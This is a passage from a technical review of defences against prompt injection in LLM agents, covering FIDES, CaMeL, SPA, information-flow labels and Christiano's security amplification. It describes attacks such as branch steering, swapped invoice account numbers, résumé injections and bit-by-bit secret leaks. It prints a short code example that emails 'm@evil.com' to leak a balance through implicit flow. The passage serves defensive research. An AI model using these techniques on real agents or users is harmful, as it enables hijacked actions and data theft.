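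To indicate what each variable holds, FIDES builds its name from the tool, a number and, where there is one, the field, as in `#read_emails_0.subject`. Developers can also restrict the planning model's output so that any variable name it writes is one that exists. FIDES hides less than the basic algorithm because it replaces part of a result with a variable only if that part is less trusted than what the planning model has already seen, so trusted fields stay readable. The planning model can also read a variable's contents when it has to, but policy checks then restrict what it may do.

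A planning model can do a lot with data it never reads. In one test, a user asked FIDES's simpler variable-passing planner to find the Slack channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. Variables hid the channels' names and the text of every message, but the planning model could still see how many messages each channel contained. One channel had no messages, so the model added Alice to it by using the variable that held its name. Hiding the text did not rule out interference, because anyone able to post in those channels could have changed the outcome by posting a message.

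In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) applied the same idea to web pages. Their software replaced the text of forum posts with variables and left the site's own buttons visible. The agent could then upvote or comment on a post without reading it, and none of the benchmark's injections succeeded.

### Writing the whole task as a program

*Code-then-execute* combines hidden data with a plan fixed in advance. The planning model writes a complete program from the user's request, and ordinary software runs it. The program for the schedule, adapted from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, is short:

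```
entries = calendar.read(today)
text = LLM("format this data", entries)
email.write(text, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The calls are the same as in the FIDES version, but here the planning model writes all three lines before the first one runs and isn't used after that. Once the program is complete, the hostile entry can't determine which actions the system takes. The best-known system of this type is CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025. Programs can contain loops and conditions, so they can handle tasks that don't fit a simple list of calls, such as the holiday notice.

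*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) restricts plans to a small language with six kinds of step: fetching a stored result, calling a tool, querying the quarantined model, showing something to the user, branching and looping. Because the language is limited, software can check the entire plan before any of it runs. If a plan fails the check, SPA drops the request instead of requesting a better plan, because a planning model that was allowed to retry could keep revising an unsafe plan until one version passed.

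SPA also keeps results from one request to the next. Suppose a user has the agent fetch an invoice on Monday and on Tuesday says, "Pay the invoice we discussed yesterday." The planning model needs some indication that the invoice exists, but showing it the invoice would expose it to whatever the invoice contains. SPA shows the model only a description of the invoice, which the model wrote on Monday before any tool had run.

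The planning model normally reads the names and descriptions of its tools, and a hostile toolmaker can put an injection there. In an optional mode of SPA, the planning model instead works out from the request alone what tools it would need, and a separate stage matches these imagined tools to real ones. If the match fails, the request fails too, and this happened often enough in tests to be the mode's main limitation.

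Conditions make programs more useful but give an attacker a new target, the choice of branch. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) describes a system of this kind for agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planning model can't see the screen, so it has to write a branch for everything that might appear there, such as a cookie notice or a login page. A quarantined vision model reads the screen, and the program picks a branch based on its output. These programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and about 4 branches for programs written for AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and messaging tasks.

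An attacker cannot add an action to such a program, but a misleading picture or button can make the vision model return a false result, which sends the program down a branch meant for a different situation. Foerster and colleagues call this *branch steering* and showed that it could take an agent to a malicious website. Rules about particular tools do little to prevent it. A rule can forbid emailing strangers, but a click's effect depends on what is under the pointer, so the same call might log the user in or delete a file.

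### A safe plan with false contents

In every version of the schedule task, the attacker keeps some control over the text the boss receives. If a quarantined model writes that text, the hostile entry can make the model leave out a meeting or add a request to approve a payment. The email comes from the user's own account, so the boss has good reason to believe it.

Costa and colleagues accept that hostile text can still affect what their quarantined model returns, such as when an email makes it return an empty summary. In one of AgentDojo's attacks, the injection only tries to make the agent recommend a particular destination to the user. Costa and colleagues don't count this as a successful prompt injection, because the agent's actions don't change and no secret gets out, although a user might still act on the advice and book a bad hotel. They suggest that the user interface could mark such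 text as untrusted or block it.

Tampering with an argument does more damage when the argument decides where something goes. In Girrens and Wang's invoice example, the attacker has put their own bank account number on the invoice. The agent looks up the invoice, extracts the account number and pays the bill as the user asked, and the money goes to the attacker. Because the attack doesn't need an instruction, a detector that looks for suspicious commands would find only an account number, and even a model with perfect resistance to injection could make the same payment.

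*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) explains formally why a fixed plan cannot help here. It compares two agents that have the same plan and differ only in that one's model may also obey calls it finds in untrusted text. A false account number leads both to pay the wrong person, so preventing the model from deviating from the plan does not prevent the mistake.

Researchers who build these systems often exclude such attacks from their guarantees. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) proposes code-then-execute for web agents, and notes that nothing guarantees that the values a model extracts from a page are correct. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) excludes manipulated outcomes from the scope of its system, Baya. The paper calls hijacked actions the most severe threat and likens them to an attacker running any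 code they choose.

That ranking makes sense for an agent with many powerful tools, because tampering with an argument can only corrupt something the user asked for. It is less convincing for an agent that pays bills, where a wrong account number in an expected payment is about the worst thing an attacker could achieve.

### Requiring trusted arguments

Costa and colleagues reply that a stricter policy check could require the arguments of a call to be trusted, as well as the decision to make it. Such a check relies on labels that record where each value came from. The software would refuse to send money to an account if the account number came from an unverified invoice.

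If the rule applies to every argument, it also blocks much of what people want from an assistant. The body of the schedule email comes from a calendar that strangers can write to, so the software would refuse to send it even when no entry is hostile. The assistant could include only appointments the user had entered, but the boss would then get an incomplete schedule. Forwarding an email or sending somebody a summary of a web page fails for the same reason.

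Costa and colleagues expected that accepting only trusted text could make FIDES much less useful. Their main tests do not measure this loss, because the policy they used for consequential actions checked whether the decision to call a tool was trusted but ignored the trust labels on the tool's arguments. Girrens and Wang measured such a loss in SPA, which rejects a whole plan if one argument is insufficiently trusted. With these checks and SPA's confidentiality checks on, no attacks on AgentDojo succeeded, but the share of ordinary tasks that SPA completed fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. On a version of the benchmark with several linked requests, it fell from 62.5% to 35.3%. Girrens and Wang attribute the loss mainly to plans that passed untrusted tool results to actions requiring trusted ones.

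A developer can preserve more functionality by setting trust requirements separately for each argument of a tool call. FIDES can require a trusted recipient while allowing an untrusted message, which works well for the schedule because an attacker can corrupt the text but not change who receives it. This doesn't help with the invoice, because the account number is the argument that most needs to be trusted, and it appears only in the invoice.

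Deciding argument by argument also leaves the contents of messages open, as Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane (2026), in *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, found with IntentFlow. Their software checks each proposed call before it runs. Arguments that decide whom or what a call reaches must match what the user asked for and come from a permitted source, while message text may come from documents. They tested it on 200 synthetic attacks:

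| What the attack altered | Attacks | Succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Recipient, attachment, participants, file path or service address | 134 | 0 |
| Database query | 34 | 0 |
| Date of an event | 8 | 0 |
| Subject of an email | 8 | 8 |
| Description of an event | 8 | 8 |
| Contents of a file | 8 | 8 |

The zeros depend on favourable conditions. The benchmark supplied the correct list of what the user had authorised, marked the documents that contained injections and stated which arguments needed the strict check. Ameur and colleagues also tested software that had to identify which of 150 arguments of outside tools needed that check. It missed about a quarter of the arguments that decide whom or what a call reaches, and missed arguments skip the check.

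A trusted source can also supply the wrong value. Suppose the user asks to write to their manager and the planning model picks the legal team's address from the company directory. The directory is trustworthy, so a check on sources alone lets the mistake through, as it did in all 50 such cases in the test. IntentFlow blocked all 50 by comparing the address with the request.

The comparison is difficult because people rarely type out addresses and instead write phrases such as "my boss". Ameur and colleagues also tried a simple check, modelled on CaMeL, that accepted a value only if it appeared word for word in the request. It stopped the same 50 errors but also rejected 16 of 50 legitimate tasks in which the user had referred to a person or service by another name. IntentFlow completed all 50 because it had a hand-compiled directory that translated phrases such as "my manager" into addresses,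 but someone has to keep such a directory correct.

When no trusted source has the value, the system can ask the user. Kolluri and colleagues' agent, Prudentia, can ask the user to approve a piece of untrusted data instead of each action based on it. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can approve the email once rather than approve ten separate tool calls. But the approval covers the whole email, including text the user may not notice, such as white letters on a white background, and the planning model then reads all of it as trusted text.

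## How much can safely pass through a narrow channel?

In many tasks, the planning model must know one fact about an email before it can choose its next tool call. A system can keep the email hidden in a variable and show the model only that fact, in a format too small to hold an instruction.

### Create a meeting only if somebody asks for one

Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an assistant to read the top three emails in the mailbox and create a calendar event if any of them contains a meeting request. This is a *data-dependent task*, meaning that the right sequence of tool calls depends on the content of the data. Here, the assistant should call the calendar tool only if it finds a request.

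A planning model that only passes variables around can't do the task, even with a quarantined model to help, because the quarantined model's answer also comes back as a variable. FIDES solves this by letting the planning model request an answer in a fixed format and then read that answer:

```
read_emails(number=3)                             -> #read_emails_0
query_llm("Is there a meeting request?",
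          #read_emails_0, output="bool")          -> #query_llm_0
inspect(#query_llm_0)                             -> true
query_llm("Extract the event details",
          #read_emails_0, output="event details") -> #query_llm_1
set_event(#query_llm_1)
```

The planning model receives information derived from the emails only through the `inspect` call, which returns either "true" or "false". If it returns "true", the quarantined model reads the emails again and extracts the date, time and participants. The planning model passes these details to the calendar without seeing them.

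Unless the format is enforced, a quarantined model under an attacker's control might answer the yes-or-no question with a paragraph of instructions. *Constrained decoding* prevents this. A language model writes one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and computes a probability for every possible next token. Before each choice, ordinary code rules out the tokens that would break the required format. For a yes-or-no question, that leaves "true" and "false". The attacker may control which one the model picks, but cannot make it write anything else.

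Costa and colleagues acknowledge that this plan technically breaks their strict rule, under which a tool call is safe only if the model based it on trusted sources. They relax the rule for Booleans (values that are either true or false) because a Boolean on its own is unlikely to lead to a prompt injection. Their benchmark results don't test this relaxation, because they left constrained decoding out of the version of FIDES they ran on AgentDojo, where most tasks did not need it.

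### One model per document

In the meeting task, one quarantined model reads all three emails together, so a hostile email could make it overlook a genuine request in another. The *map-reduce* design keeps the documents apart. In the "map" step, a separate isolated model reads each document and returns a small answer, and the "reduce" step combines the answers.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that has to find this month's invoices among a user's files and email them to the accounting department. If a single model reads all the files, a malicious instruction in one of them can make it collect other files and send them to an attacker. With map-reduce, a separate model reads each file and outputs whether it contains an invoice, and another model then writes and sends the email. An attacker can still get a malicious file marked as an invoice, but they could also get a file marked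 that way by submitting a real invoice.

The reduce step can be ordinary code or a model with tools, provided that software checks the format of every answer it receives. In the invoice case, the model that sends the email must attach the files without opening them, because opening them could expose it to the injection again. It should also refer to the files by number, because an attacker who supplies a file can put an instruction in its name.

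The same design works for product reviews and job applications. A shopping assistant that reads all reviews together is vulnerable to a review containing an instruction to recommend a rival product. If a separate model instead reduces each review to fixed categories, such as "good price" or "easy to use", ordinary code can count them. A dishonest reviewer can still get every category ticked for their own product, but can't affect how the system reads other reviews. A hidden instruction in a résumé to ignore everyone who worked for a certain company also fails, because the model that reads the résumé sees no other candidates. The applicant can still falsely claim 20 years of experience and take an honest candidate's place on the shortlist. Isolation limits what each document can do but doesn't limit how many an attacker submits, so someone who posts 500 fake reviews controls 500 sets of answers.

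Some tasks don't divide in this way. To find out whether two contracts contradict each other, a model generally has to read both. Whoever designs the format also has to predict what information will matter. In the shopping example, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that users may not know which categories are relevant to a product they have never bought, though they could ask a model to suggest some.

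Richer formats lose less information. The medical chatbot from the previous section could record a patient's symptoms in a form with no free-text fields. According to Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, this leaves no room for an injection in the summary and keeps most of the chatbot's usefulness, as long as symptoms fit a rigid form. In their safest design for a coding agent, a quarantined model converts third-party code and documentation into a strictly formatted list of the available functions, with names of at most 30 characters, for example. The coding agent never sees explanations or examples, which programmers rely on heavily.

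A yes-or-no answer protects the planning model only if the model never sees the original text. Some chatbots use a classifier to decide whether a customer's message is on topic and, if it is, pass the whole message to the model. If the topic is furniture, an attacker can get an unrelated instruction to the model by combining it with a question about furniture.

### Counting bits

A format that allows *m* different answers can carry at most log₂(*m*) bits of information, so a yes-or-no answer can carry at most 1 bit. If the planning model asks *k* yes-or-no questions, there are 2^*k* possible sets of answers, which carry up to *k* bits. The total is lower when one answer partly determines another.

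Suppose each character in the function names can be one of 26 lower-case letters, 26 capitals, ten digits or an underscore. That makes 63 symbols, so a 30-character name can carry 30 × log₂(63), or about 179 bits.

| What the planning model reads | Possible messages | Limit in bits |
|---|---|---|
| One yes or no | 2 | 1 |
| A choice among 3 tasks | 3 | 1.6 |
| A choice among 16 categories | 16 | 4 |
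| Ten yes-or-no answers | 1,024 | 10 |
| A 30-character function name | about 10⁵⁴ | 179 |
| Free text | no fixed limit | no fixed limit |

A developer can check a small format exhaustively. With ten yes-or-no answers, the developer can run the planning model on all 1,024 combinations, several times each if its output varies, and look at what it does. Testing all 10⁵⁴ possible names this way is impossible.

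A function name can also hold an instruction. `delete_all_files_then_continue` is exactly 30 characters long, and a list of 20 functions has room for 20 names of that length. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think an injection is unlikely to survive this kind of formatting if the requirements are strict enough. They may well be right, since a model has little reason to treat a function's name as a command, but this is again a judgement about how the model will behave. Replacing the names with `function_1`, `function_2` and so on would remove the doubt, but the agent would lose most of its information about what the functions do.

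FIDES includes the format in the label it attaches to each piece of data. Costa and colleagues order the formats by their capacity:

```
bool  ⊑  enum["a", "b", "c"]  ⊑  string
```

An `enum` is a choice from a fixed list, a `string` is free text, and ⊑ here means "can carry no more information than". A policy check can use this part of the label to allow a consequential action after the planning model has read an untrusted Boolean, but block it after the model has read an untrusted string. When the system combines two pieces of data, the result gets the larger format, so a Boolean combined with a string counts as a string.

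This ordering does not account for repetition. Under the combination rule, two Booleans together still have the label of one Boolean, because neither format is larger. After 179 yes-or-no questions about an email, the planning model could have received as much information as a 30-character name holds, but its context would still have the label for a single bit. An email can't dictate the planning model's questions, so a long series of them is unlikely in a simple task. In a long task, a developer who wants to limit the total information needs a counter as well as a label.

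### What one bit can decide

A channel's capacity in bits limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose between, but not how bad those outcomes are. Suppose a user tells an assistant, "If the supplier's email says the goods have shipped, pay the remaining €40,000." The planning model needs only 1 bit from the email, but a dishonest supplier can trigger the payment by lying about the goods, without any prompt injection. Choosing among 1,024 songs takes 10 bits, yet an attacker who controls all of them can only make the assistant play a song the user doesn't want.

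The small format still helps in the payment case. If the amount and the account number come from the user, the supplier can trigger only the payment the user intended, though perhaps before the goods exist. An injection in the same email could make an ordinary agent pay a different sum to somebody else. The user could reduce the remaining risk of paying too early by making the payment depend on the warehouse's own records.

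Developers therefore have to examine the worst outcome that a format allows. Costa and colleagues suggest that a quarantined model could also choose from a list of tasks, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding the email. A choice among these three tasks carries less than 1.6 bits, but a hostile sender can always make the model choose forwarding. If the user has fixed the recipient, forwarding the email might only add a little clutter to that person's inbox. Forwarding is much more dangerous if the recipient's address comes from the email itself.

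In the meeting task, the 1-bit limit applies only to what the planning model reads. The event's details go to the calendar in a variable, so an attacker can still control them, as with the text of the schedule email. A hostile email can create a meeting with any title, time and participants.

Small answers can also leak secrets. Suppose a quarantined model has access to a hostile email and the user's four-digit PIN, and the attacker can see whether the assistant accepts a meeting. There are 10,000 possible PINs, or about 13.3 bits, so 14 such decisions are enough to reveal the whole number. A single decision can reveal a yes-or-no secret, such as whether a company is about to be sold.

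### Splitting a question until no piece is dangerous

A related idea came from AI alignment, the study of how to make AI systems do what people want. In 2016, before language models could use tools, the researcher Paul Christiano described a problem called *security amplification*. It was part of a plan for training AI systems on questions too hard for one person to judge. A person, the *overseer*, would work on each question with many AI assistants. A new model would learn to imitate the whole group, copies of that model would form the next group, and so on.

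An assistant that learns from a person can inherit the person's weaknesses. Christiano used "attack" to mean any series of messages that makes an agent stop cooperating, such as a clever argument that persuades it to sabotage the work. Taking a vote among ten copies of the agent doesn't help, because all ten read the same argument and fall for it. Security amplification means combining the copies into a group that is harder to attack than any of its members.

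Christiano proposed that no member should read the whole input. A member might receive the message "the sentence with the list of words [x]", where [x] points to words that other members have seen and can answer questions about. FIDES uses variables in a similar way. In one of Christiano's examples, an agent fails whenever it sees the phrase "not playing solitaire". If a different copy of the agent handles each word, the group might work out what the sentence means without any copy seeing the phrase.

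The argument that this could make the group safer depends on two quantities. One is the complexity of the simplest attack on a single agent, *k*ᴬ. The other, *k*⁰, is the complexity of the simplest questions that still suffice, meaning that the group can answer everything else by breaking it down into them. The argument then goes like this:

1. The group can split any question more complex than *k*⁰ into strictly simpler ones.
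2. *k*⁰ is lower than *k*ᴬ.
3. The group can therefore keep splitting until every piece is simpler than *k*ᴬ. Each piece is then safe, because no attack is that simple.
4. An attack on the group must therefore be more complex than the simplest attack on one agent. If a new model learns to imitate the group, copies of it can form a group that is harder still to attack.

Christiano tentatively defined the complexity of a question *Q* as −log µ(*Q*), where µ(*Q*) is the probability that a certain random procedure produces *Q*. With base-2 logarithms, the unit is again the bit, so a question with a probability of 1 in 1,024 has a complexity of 10 bits. Half the time, the procedure generates a question and then picks one of the subquestions that come up in answering it, so subquestions that help answer many questions count as simple.

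Suppose answering a question takes *N* subquestions. Under one definition, a subquestion is simpler than the original if nobody who saw it could guess the original with probability above 1/(2*N*). With 16 subquestions, each has to leave out about 5 bits of information about the original. "When did this happen?" easily meets that condition, since it could come from a question about the causes of the Great Depression, the effects of the Spanish flu or many other things. Christiano was sure this was not the right definition and expected somebody to find a better one.

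The second step is the open assumption, but it is partly testable because people can search for simple attacks. Christiano estimated that ten people could try about two million questions a year, and that a search aimed at likely attacks would find them 10 to 1,000 times as often as random sampling. On that basis, he felt fairly safe assuming that 10⁸ random questions would contain no attack on a careful, well-briefed person. He felt unsafe assuming the same of 10³⁰ questions, and didn't know where in between attacks would begin to appear.

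These figures equal about 27 and 100 bits. The 30-character function name, at 179 bits, far exceeds both. The comparison is rough, because the estimates concern human overseers and a language model may fail on much simpler inputs.

### What a low-bandwidth overseer may be unable to do

It is much harder to test whether questions this small are enough. Participants in the discussions that followed distinguished two kinds of overseer. A *high-bandwidth* overseer is a person who has between 15 minutes and a day to study the input and can read as much of it as time allows. A *low-bandwidth* overseer handles only messages from a fixed, finite set and passes everything else along unread. A set of 10⁸ to 10³⁰ messages corresponds to messages of roughly two to seven arbitrary words from a vocabulary of 10,000.

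Since a low-bandwidth overseer can receive only a finite set of messages, someone could in principle record its response to each one and replace the overseer with the resulting table. If no number of copies of that table could do a task together, the overseer can't do it either.

Some skills may be lost when a task is split into small pieces. For example, a person who speaks French and English can translate a sentence after reading all of it, but usually can't explain the skill well enough for others to apply it word by word. Christiano accepted that splitting the task would make the translation worse. After enough rounds, the system might not know French at all and could only recommend consulting a dictionary.

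He thought this might be acceptable if the system learned to use outside help safely, for instance by hiring a translator. He was also more hopeful about some other skills that seem hard to divide. In a game he tried three times, two debaters argued about what an image showed, making claims about smaller and smaller details, such as ears, lines and angles, until the judge had to check only one pixel. He believed the honest debater could win quite easily, which would mean that judgements about a whole image can rest on very small pieces of it.

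Christiano offered $10,000 in prizes for the best arguments that his approach was doomed. Wei Dai, who had also proposed the translation example, won half of it for *Can corrigibility be learned safely?* and the discussion around it. Corrigibility here roughly means being disposed to help the people you work for and to let them correct you. Dai argues that an overseer who learns corrigibility in small pieces will be too literal, and will lack a common-sense understanding of language and independent judgement about what the user wants and needs. A large enough group of such overseers could learn these things from outside sources, but it would have to decide which sources to trust before it had much judgement of its own.

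This objection is more serious than the loss of translation. A system can buy a translation, but if it misunderstands what its user wants, it may also misunderstand the help it gets. Christiano regarded it as an open question whether the small pieces can add up to good judgement, and the objection does not rule that out. He later added a note that his method of splitting could not work on its own, though he still found the basic approach plausible.

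A group can also go wrong when all its members behave well. Suppose one of them splits the question "What should I do for the user?" into "What are the user's values?" and "What action is best according to those values?" Both questions look harmless, but the group then acts on an imperfect description of the user's values as if it were exact, and no longer has a reason to check it.

*AI Safety in a World of Vulnerable Machine Learning Systems* (2023), from the research nonprofit FAR.AI, raises the possibility that if one subquestion contains an attack, its answer could "infect" the rest of the tree of questions. The members that ask these questions have a reason to avoid ones that might make them fail, so this plan is less exposed than methods that reward a model for getting approval from a fallible judge. Small fixed answer formats should also slow the spread, because a bad yes or no can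 mislead the next member but cannot carry the attack's text.

Evidence from Go suggests that adding computation doesn't always fix a weak component. KataGo, a program that plays better than any human, combines a neural network with a search through possible continuations. The search works somewhat like a group, using many of the network's judgements to reach a better one. FAR.AI's researchers trained an opponent to exploit the network's mistakes. KataGo beat the first version by searching only 32 positions, but a later version won 76% of its games even when KataGo searched ten million. This shows that some weaknesses survive a huge increase in computation, but it doesn't test Christiano's proposal, because KataGo's search doesn't split questions into tiny pieces.

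Another prize-winning objection is that an attacker could exploit the group as a whole. If its members can answer general questions by passing messages, together they can probably carry out any computation, including one that an attacker has described in the input. Attackers on ordinary software similarly chain together harmless fragments of a program's own code. No member would need to receive anything harmful, and the restriction that protects each member could also keep all of them from detecting the attack. The meeting assistant has a small version of this problem, because a planning model that receives only "true" can't detect that the meeting is at 3 a.m. with forty strangers.

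## How does a system track what untrusted data has touched?

A "true" that a model extracted from a hostile email looks the same as a "true" from the user's own notes. To treat them differently, software has to record where each piece of data came from and keep that record correct while models summarise, translate and combine the data. *Information-flow control* does this with labels. Security researchers developed it for conventional computers decades ago. FIDES, the Microsoft system whose planning model passes on variables it cannot read, applies it to agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced that developers could use FIDES in Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents.

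### Labels and joins

Each piece of data gets two labels. The *integrity* label is trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and the *confidentiality* label is public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high). Costa and colleagues order the values by how far they restrict the use of the data:

```
integrity:        T ⊑ U
confidentiality:  L ⊑ H
```

Here ⊑ means "is no more restrictive than". When software combines two pieces of data, the result takes the more restrictive value of each label. This operation is called the *join* and is written ⊔, so T ⊔ U = U and L ⊔ H = H. A report based on a trusted secret document and an untrusted public web page is therefore untrusted and secret, even if it uses only one word from the page.

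Two levels of secrecy are too few for an office, where one colleague may read a document and another may not. A confidentiality label can instead list the people who may read the data, and the join is then the intersection of the lists. Suppose A, B and C may read one file, while B, C and D may read another. Only B and C may read an email that quotes both:

```
{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}
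```

An integrity label can similarly list everyone who could have written the data. The join is then the union, because all four people could have influenced the email.

### The loop with labels

FIDES adds labels to the ordinary agent loop as follows:

1. Code labels the user's request, normally as trusted and public, and puts it in the context. The context has its own label, which is the join of the labels of everything in it.
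2. The model reads the context and proposes a tool call. The call and any arguments the model wrote inherit the context's label, because the software cannot tell which parts of the context the model relied on. An argument taken from a variable keeps the variable's label.
3. Ordinary code runs a *policy check*, which compares these labels with the rules for that tool. If the check fails, the call does not run.
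4. If the check succeeds, the tool runs. Its result gets the join of the labels of the call, the arguments and any stored data the tool read. Whatever the tool writes to storage gets the same label.
5. Code adds the result to the context and updates the context's label. If the result would make that label more restrictive, FIDES stores it in a variable instead.
6. The loop repeats until the model answers the user.

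A label can cover a whole tool result or a single field. Labelling each field lets a system trust the time stamp that the user's own mail server put on an email without trusting the subject or body.

Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for step 3. The first allows a consequential call to run only if it comes from a trusted context. The second allows a call to send data only to people allowed to read it, so every recipient of an email has to be on the reader list for its contents.

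Under the second policy alone, an injection can still make an agent send messages, but only to people who are already allowed to read their contents. Under the first alone, an agent can send secrets to anyone if it decided to do so in a trusted context. The user may want this, for example when asking an assistant to send a salary list to a new accountant. Kolluri and colleagues therefore let a tool that sends data run if it satisfies either policy, and require a trusted context for other consequential actions.

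### How one email taints a context

Suppose a user says, "Read my latest email, then delete my draft called 'Old budget'." The email is a harmless newsletter from a shop, and the agent is a basic one that does not use variables.

| Step | Integrity of the context | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The request arrives | Trusted | Everyone |
| The model calls the mail tool, and the check allows it | Trusted | Everyone |
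| The newsletter enters the context | Untrusted | The user and the shop |
| The model asks to delete the draft, and the check blocks it | Untrusted | The user and the shop |

The newsletter has produced a *tainted context*, so everything the model writes from then on counts as untrusted. The user asked for the deletion, but the software can't determine whether that request or the newsletter led the model to propose it. The agent also can't send a colleague "Lunch at noon?", because the model would write the message after reading the newsletter and the colleague is not on the newsletter's reader list.

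If the agent had deleted the draft first, both parts of the task would have worked. An agent that knows the policies can order its actions with them in mind, and Kolluri and colleagues' Prudentia is given the policies and the label of its context. Before it opens a variable, it has to explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it plans to make afterwards.

A check on the current context can miss a tool that reads confidential data and sends it out in a single call. Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, describe a test tool that opens a confidential ledger and emails it to an outside address. Before the call, the context contains nothing confidential, so a simple check allows the call. APPA works out what the context's label would be after the tool had read the ledger, and blocks the call before it runs. It checks again when a result arrives, in case the tool returned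 something its developer had not declared.

### What the labels guarantee

Costa and colleagues prove that their loop can enforce *explicit secrecy*. Take a sequence of tool calls and hold it fixed. If two sets of stored data differ only in their secrets, running that sequence on either must leave the same public data behind. In symbols, *g* is the combined effect of the calls, and =ʟ means "has the same public parts as":

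```
if d₁ =ʟ d₂, then g(d₁) =ʟ g(d₂)
```

This rules out direct flows, in which a call copies a secret, or something computed from it, to somewhere an outsider can read it. An outsider may still be able to infer a secret from which calls the agent makes. Suppose a user asks an assistant to find a clinic's page about an illness and open it only if a private test result is positive. The page's address came from a public search, so the assistant may send it out, and the request doesn't contain the test result. But whoever runs the clinic's website can infer the result from the visit.

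*Noninterference* is a stronger property that would prevent this. It requires that any two runs differing only in secrets look the same to an outsider, including in which calls the agent makes. Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive. In their loop, it would essentially mean that an agent that had used any tool that might read a secret could no longer use any tool that might write something public. For example, an assistant that had opened one private email could no longer visit a website. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones, also enforce only explicit secrecy.

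The proof also assumes that a model always gives the same output for the same input, which language models often don't do in ordinary use. It doesn't cover leaks through timing or the size of network packets.

### Leaks in earlier systems

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, looked for gaps in two leading systems, FIDES and CaMeL. CaMeL's interpreter tracks labels while it runs the planning model's program. If a program emails an outsider directly when an account balance exceeds some threshold, CaMeL blocks the email. This version, which follows a pattern known since 1974, gets through:

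```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL labels `tmp` as secret because the change depended on the balance. The fourth line then changes nothing, so `rich` is still true and still public, and the email goes out. When the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and the program sends nothing. The outsider learns whether the balance is above the threshold, because CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that the program takes.

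A second leak comes from code outside the interpreter. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop prompts the planning model to write another, and CaMeL does not track the data that passes through this loop. A secret can determine whether a policy check blocks an attempt, so the result reveals one bit of information about the secret. An attacker could repeat the loop to extract the whole secret one bit at a time. Garby and colleagues also found that inserting an untrusted value into fixed text made CaMeL treat the value as trusted.

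These flaws weaken the guarantee more than they create everyday danger. To exploit the first, an attacker has to get the planning model to write that unusual program, and in CaMeL this model does not read outside text. But people adopt such a system because they want a guarantee, and CaMeL has no proof that its tracking is sound. Its developers call formalising it a "crucial direction" for further work.

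Garby and colleagues object to the deliberate exceptions in FIDES. FIDES ignores what outsiders can infer from the agent's choices, and a policy may let an untrusted Boolean influence a consequential action. Each exception is defensible, but someone auditing a particular run cannot tell whether a value that got through was a harmless exception or a real leak.

### A calculus with a proof

Their alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents based on the lambda calculus, a minimal language that theorists use to reason about programs. Every value has a label that each step of the computation updates. The interpreter also keeps a label for the branch it is executing. The program cannot add a message to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret.

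Garby and colleagues prove noninterference for every program in the language that does not deliberately relabel data, including programs that a model writes while the agent runs. Because models are partly random, the theorem compares the probabilities of different results. As is common in this field, it still allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes. The proof checker Lean has verified the theorem, which covers the same interpreter that calls the model.

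In a loop with only one conversation, a single secret affects every later decision. An LLMbda program can instead ask its question in a temporary copy of the conversation and then discard the copy, so the secret restricts only what depends on the answer. This weakens the case against noninterference.

The researchers built an agent in LLMbda called Randori. Its model writes a program and tests it on artificial data, revising it until it runs. The agent then runs the program on the real account. If the model tested on real data instead, an error message derived from that data could taint the next attempt. The researchers tested Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with nine attacks on each, using three models and three repetitions. Two of the 1,296 attacks succeeded.

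Part of that result came from fixing the program in advance rather than from the labels. In 97 of the 144 pairs of task and attack, the attack needed a tool call or file that a program written for the user's task would never include, so fixing the program was generally enough to stop it. Both of the attacker's successes came from one pair, in which the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Labelling the file as untrusted doesn't show whether the bill in it is genuine.

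### Trusting untrusted data on purpose

Once a context is tainted, nothing the agent reads can remove the taint, because a join never makes a label less restrictive. Kravchenko and colleagues call agents in this position "stranded" and prove that further reading cannot unblock a call that the taint has blocked, so someone has to grant an exception.

*Endorsement* changes the label of a piece of data from untrusted to trusted. In Kolluri and colleagues' example of the emailed to-do list, endorsement lets one approval replace ten, because the context stays trusted after the agent reads the email. When no consequential action will follow, Prudentia can skip asking for approval and let the context become untrusted. On AgentDojo, Prudentia needed up to 1.9 times fewer human approvals than FIDES.

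Kolluri and colleagues left out the corresponding operation for secrets, *declassification*, which would let more people read a piece of data. Whether it is acceptable to share private data depends heavily on the situation, so they have the user approve each call that would send it.

A program can also endorse data. In LLMbda's example, a quarantined model sorts an email into one of a few categories, code checks that the answer is on the list, and the program endorses it for use as the subject of a reply. The attacker can then choose among the categories but can't write the subject. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement in LLMbda cannot expose secrets, even if the attacker wrote the endorsed data. However, endorsing data gives up protection against its influence on actions.

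Randori's planning model writes its endorsements before it receives any outside data. In runs without attacks, the agent using Qwen3.7-plus completed 36 of 48 with endorsements, compared with 30 when the researchers removed the ability to endorse data. But endorsements also let the two false payments through, and the language does not stop a planning model from endorsing everything.

APPA offers two narrower exceptions. A person, a fixed rule or another model can authorise one exact call without changing the context's label or affecting later calls. Alternatively, the agent can open a disposable branch, which is a copy of the conversation. The branch reads the untrusted text, becomes tainted and returns an answer in a fixed format, while the main conversation keeps its old label. Hostile text can still make the branch return a wrong answer in the correct format, so Kravchenko and colleagues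 leave the developer to decide whether to trust the answer.

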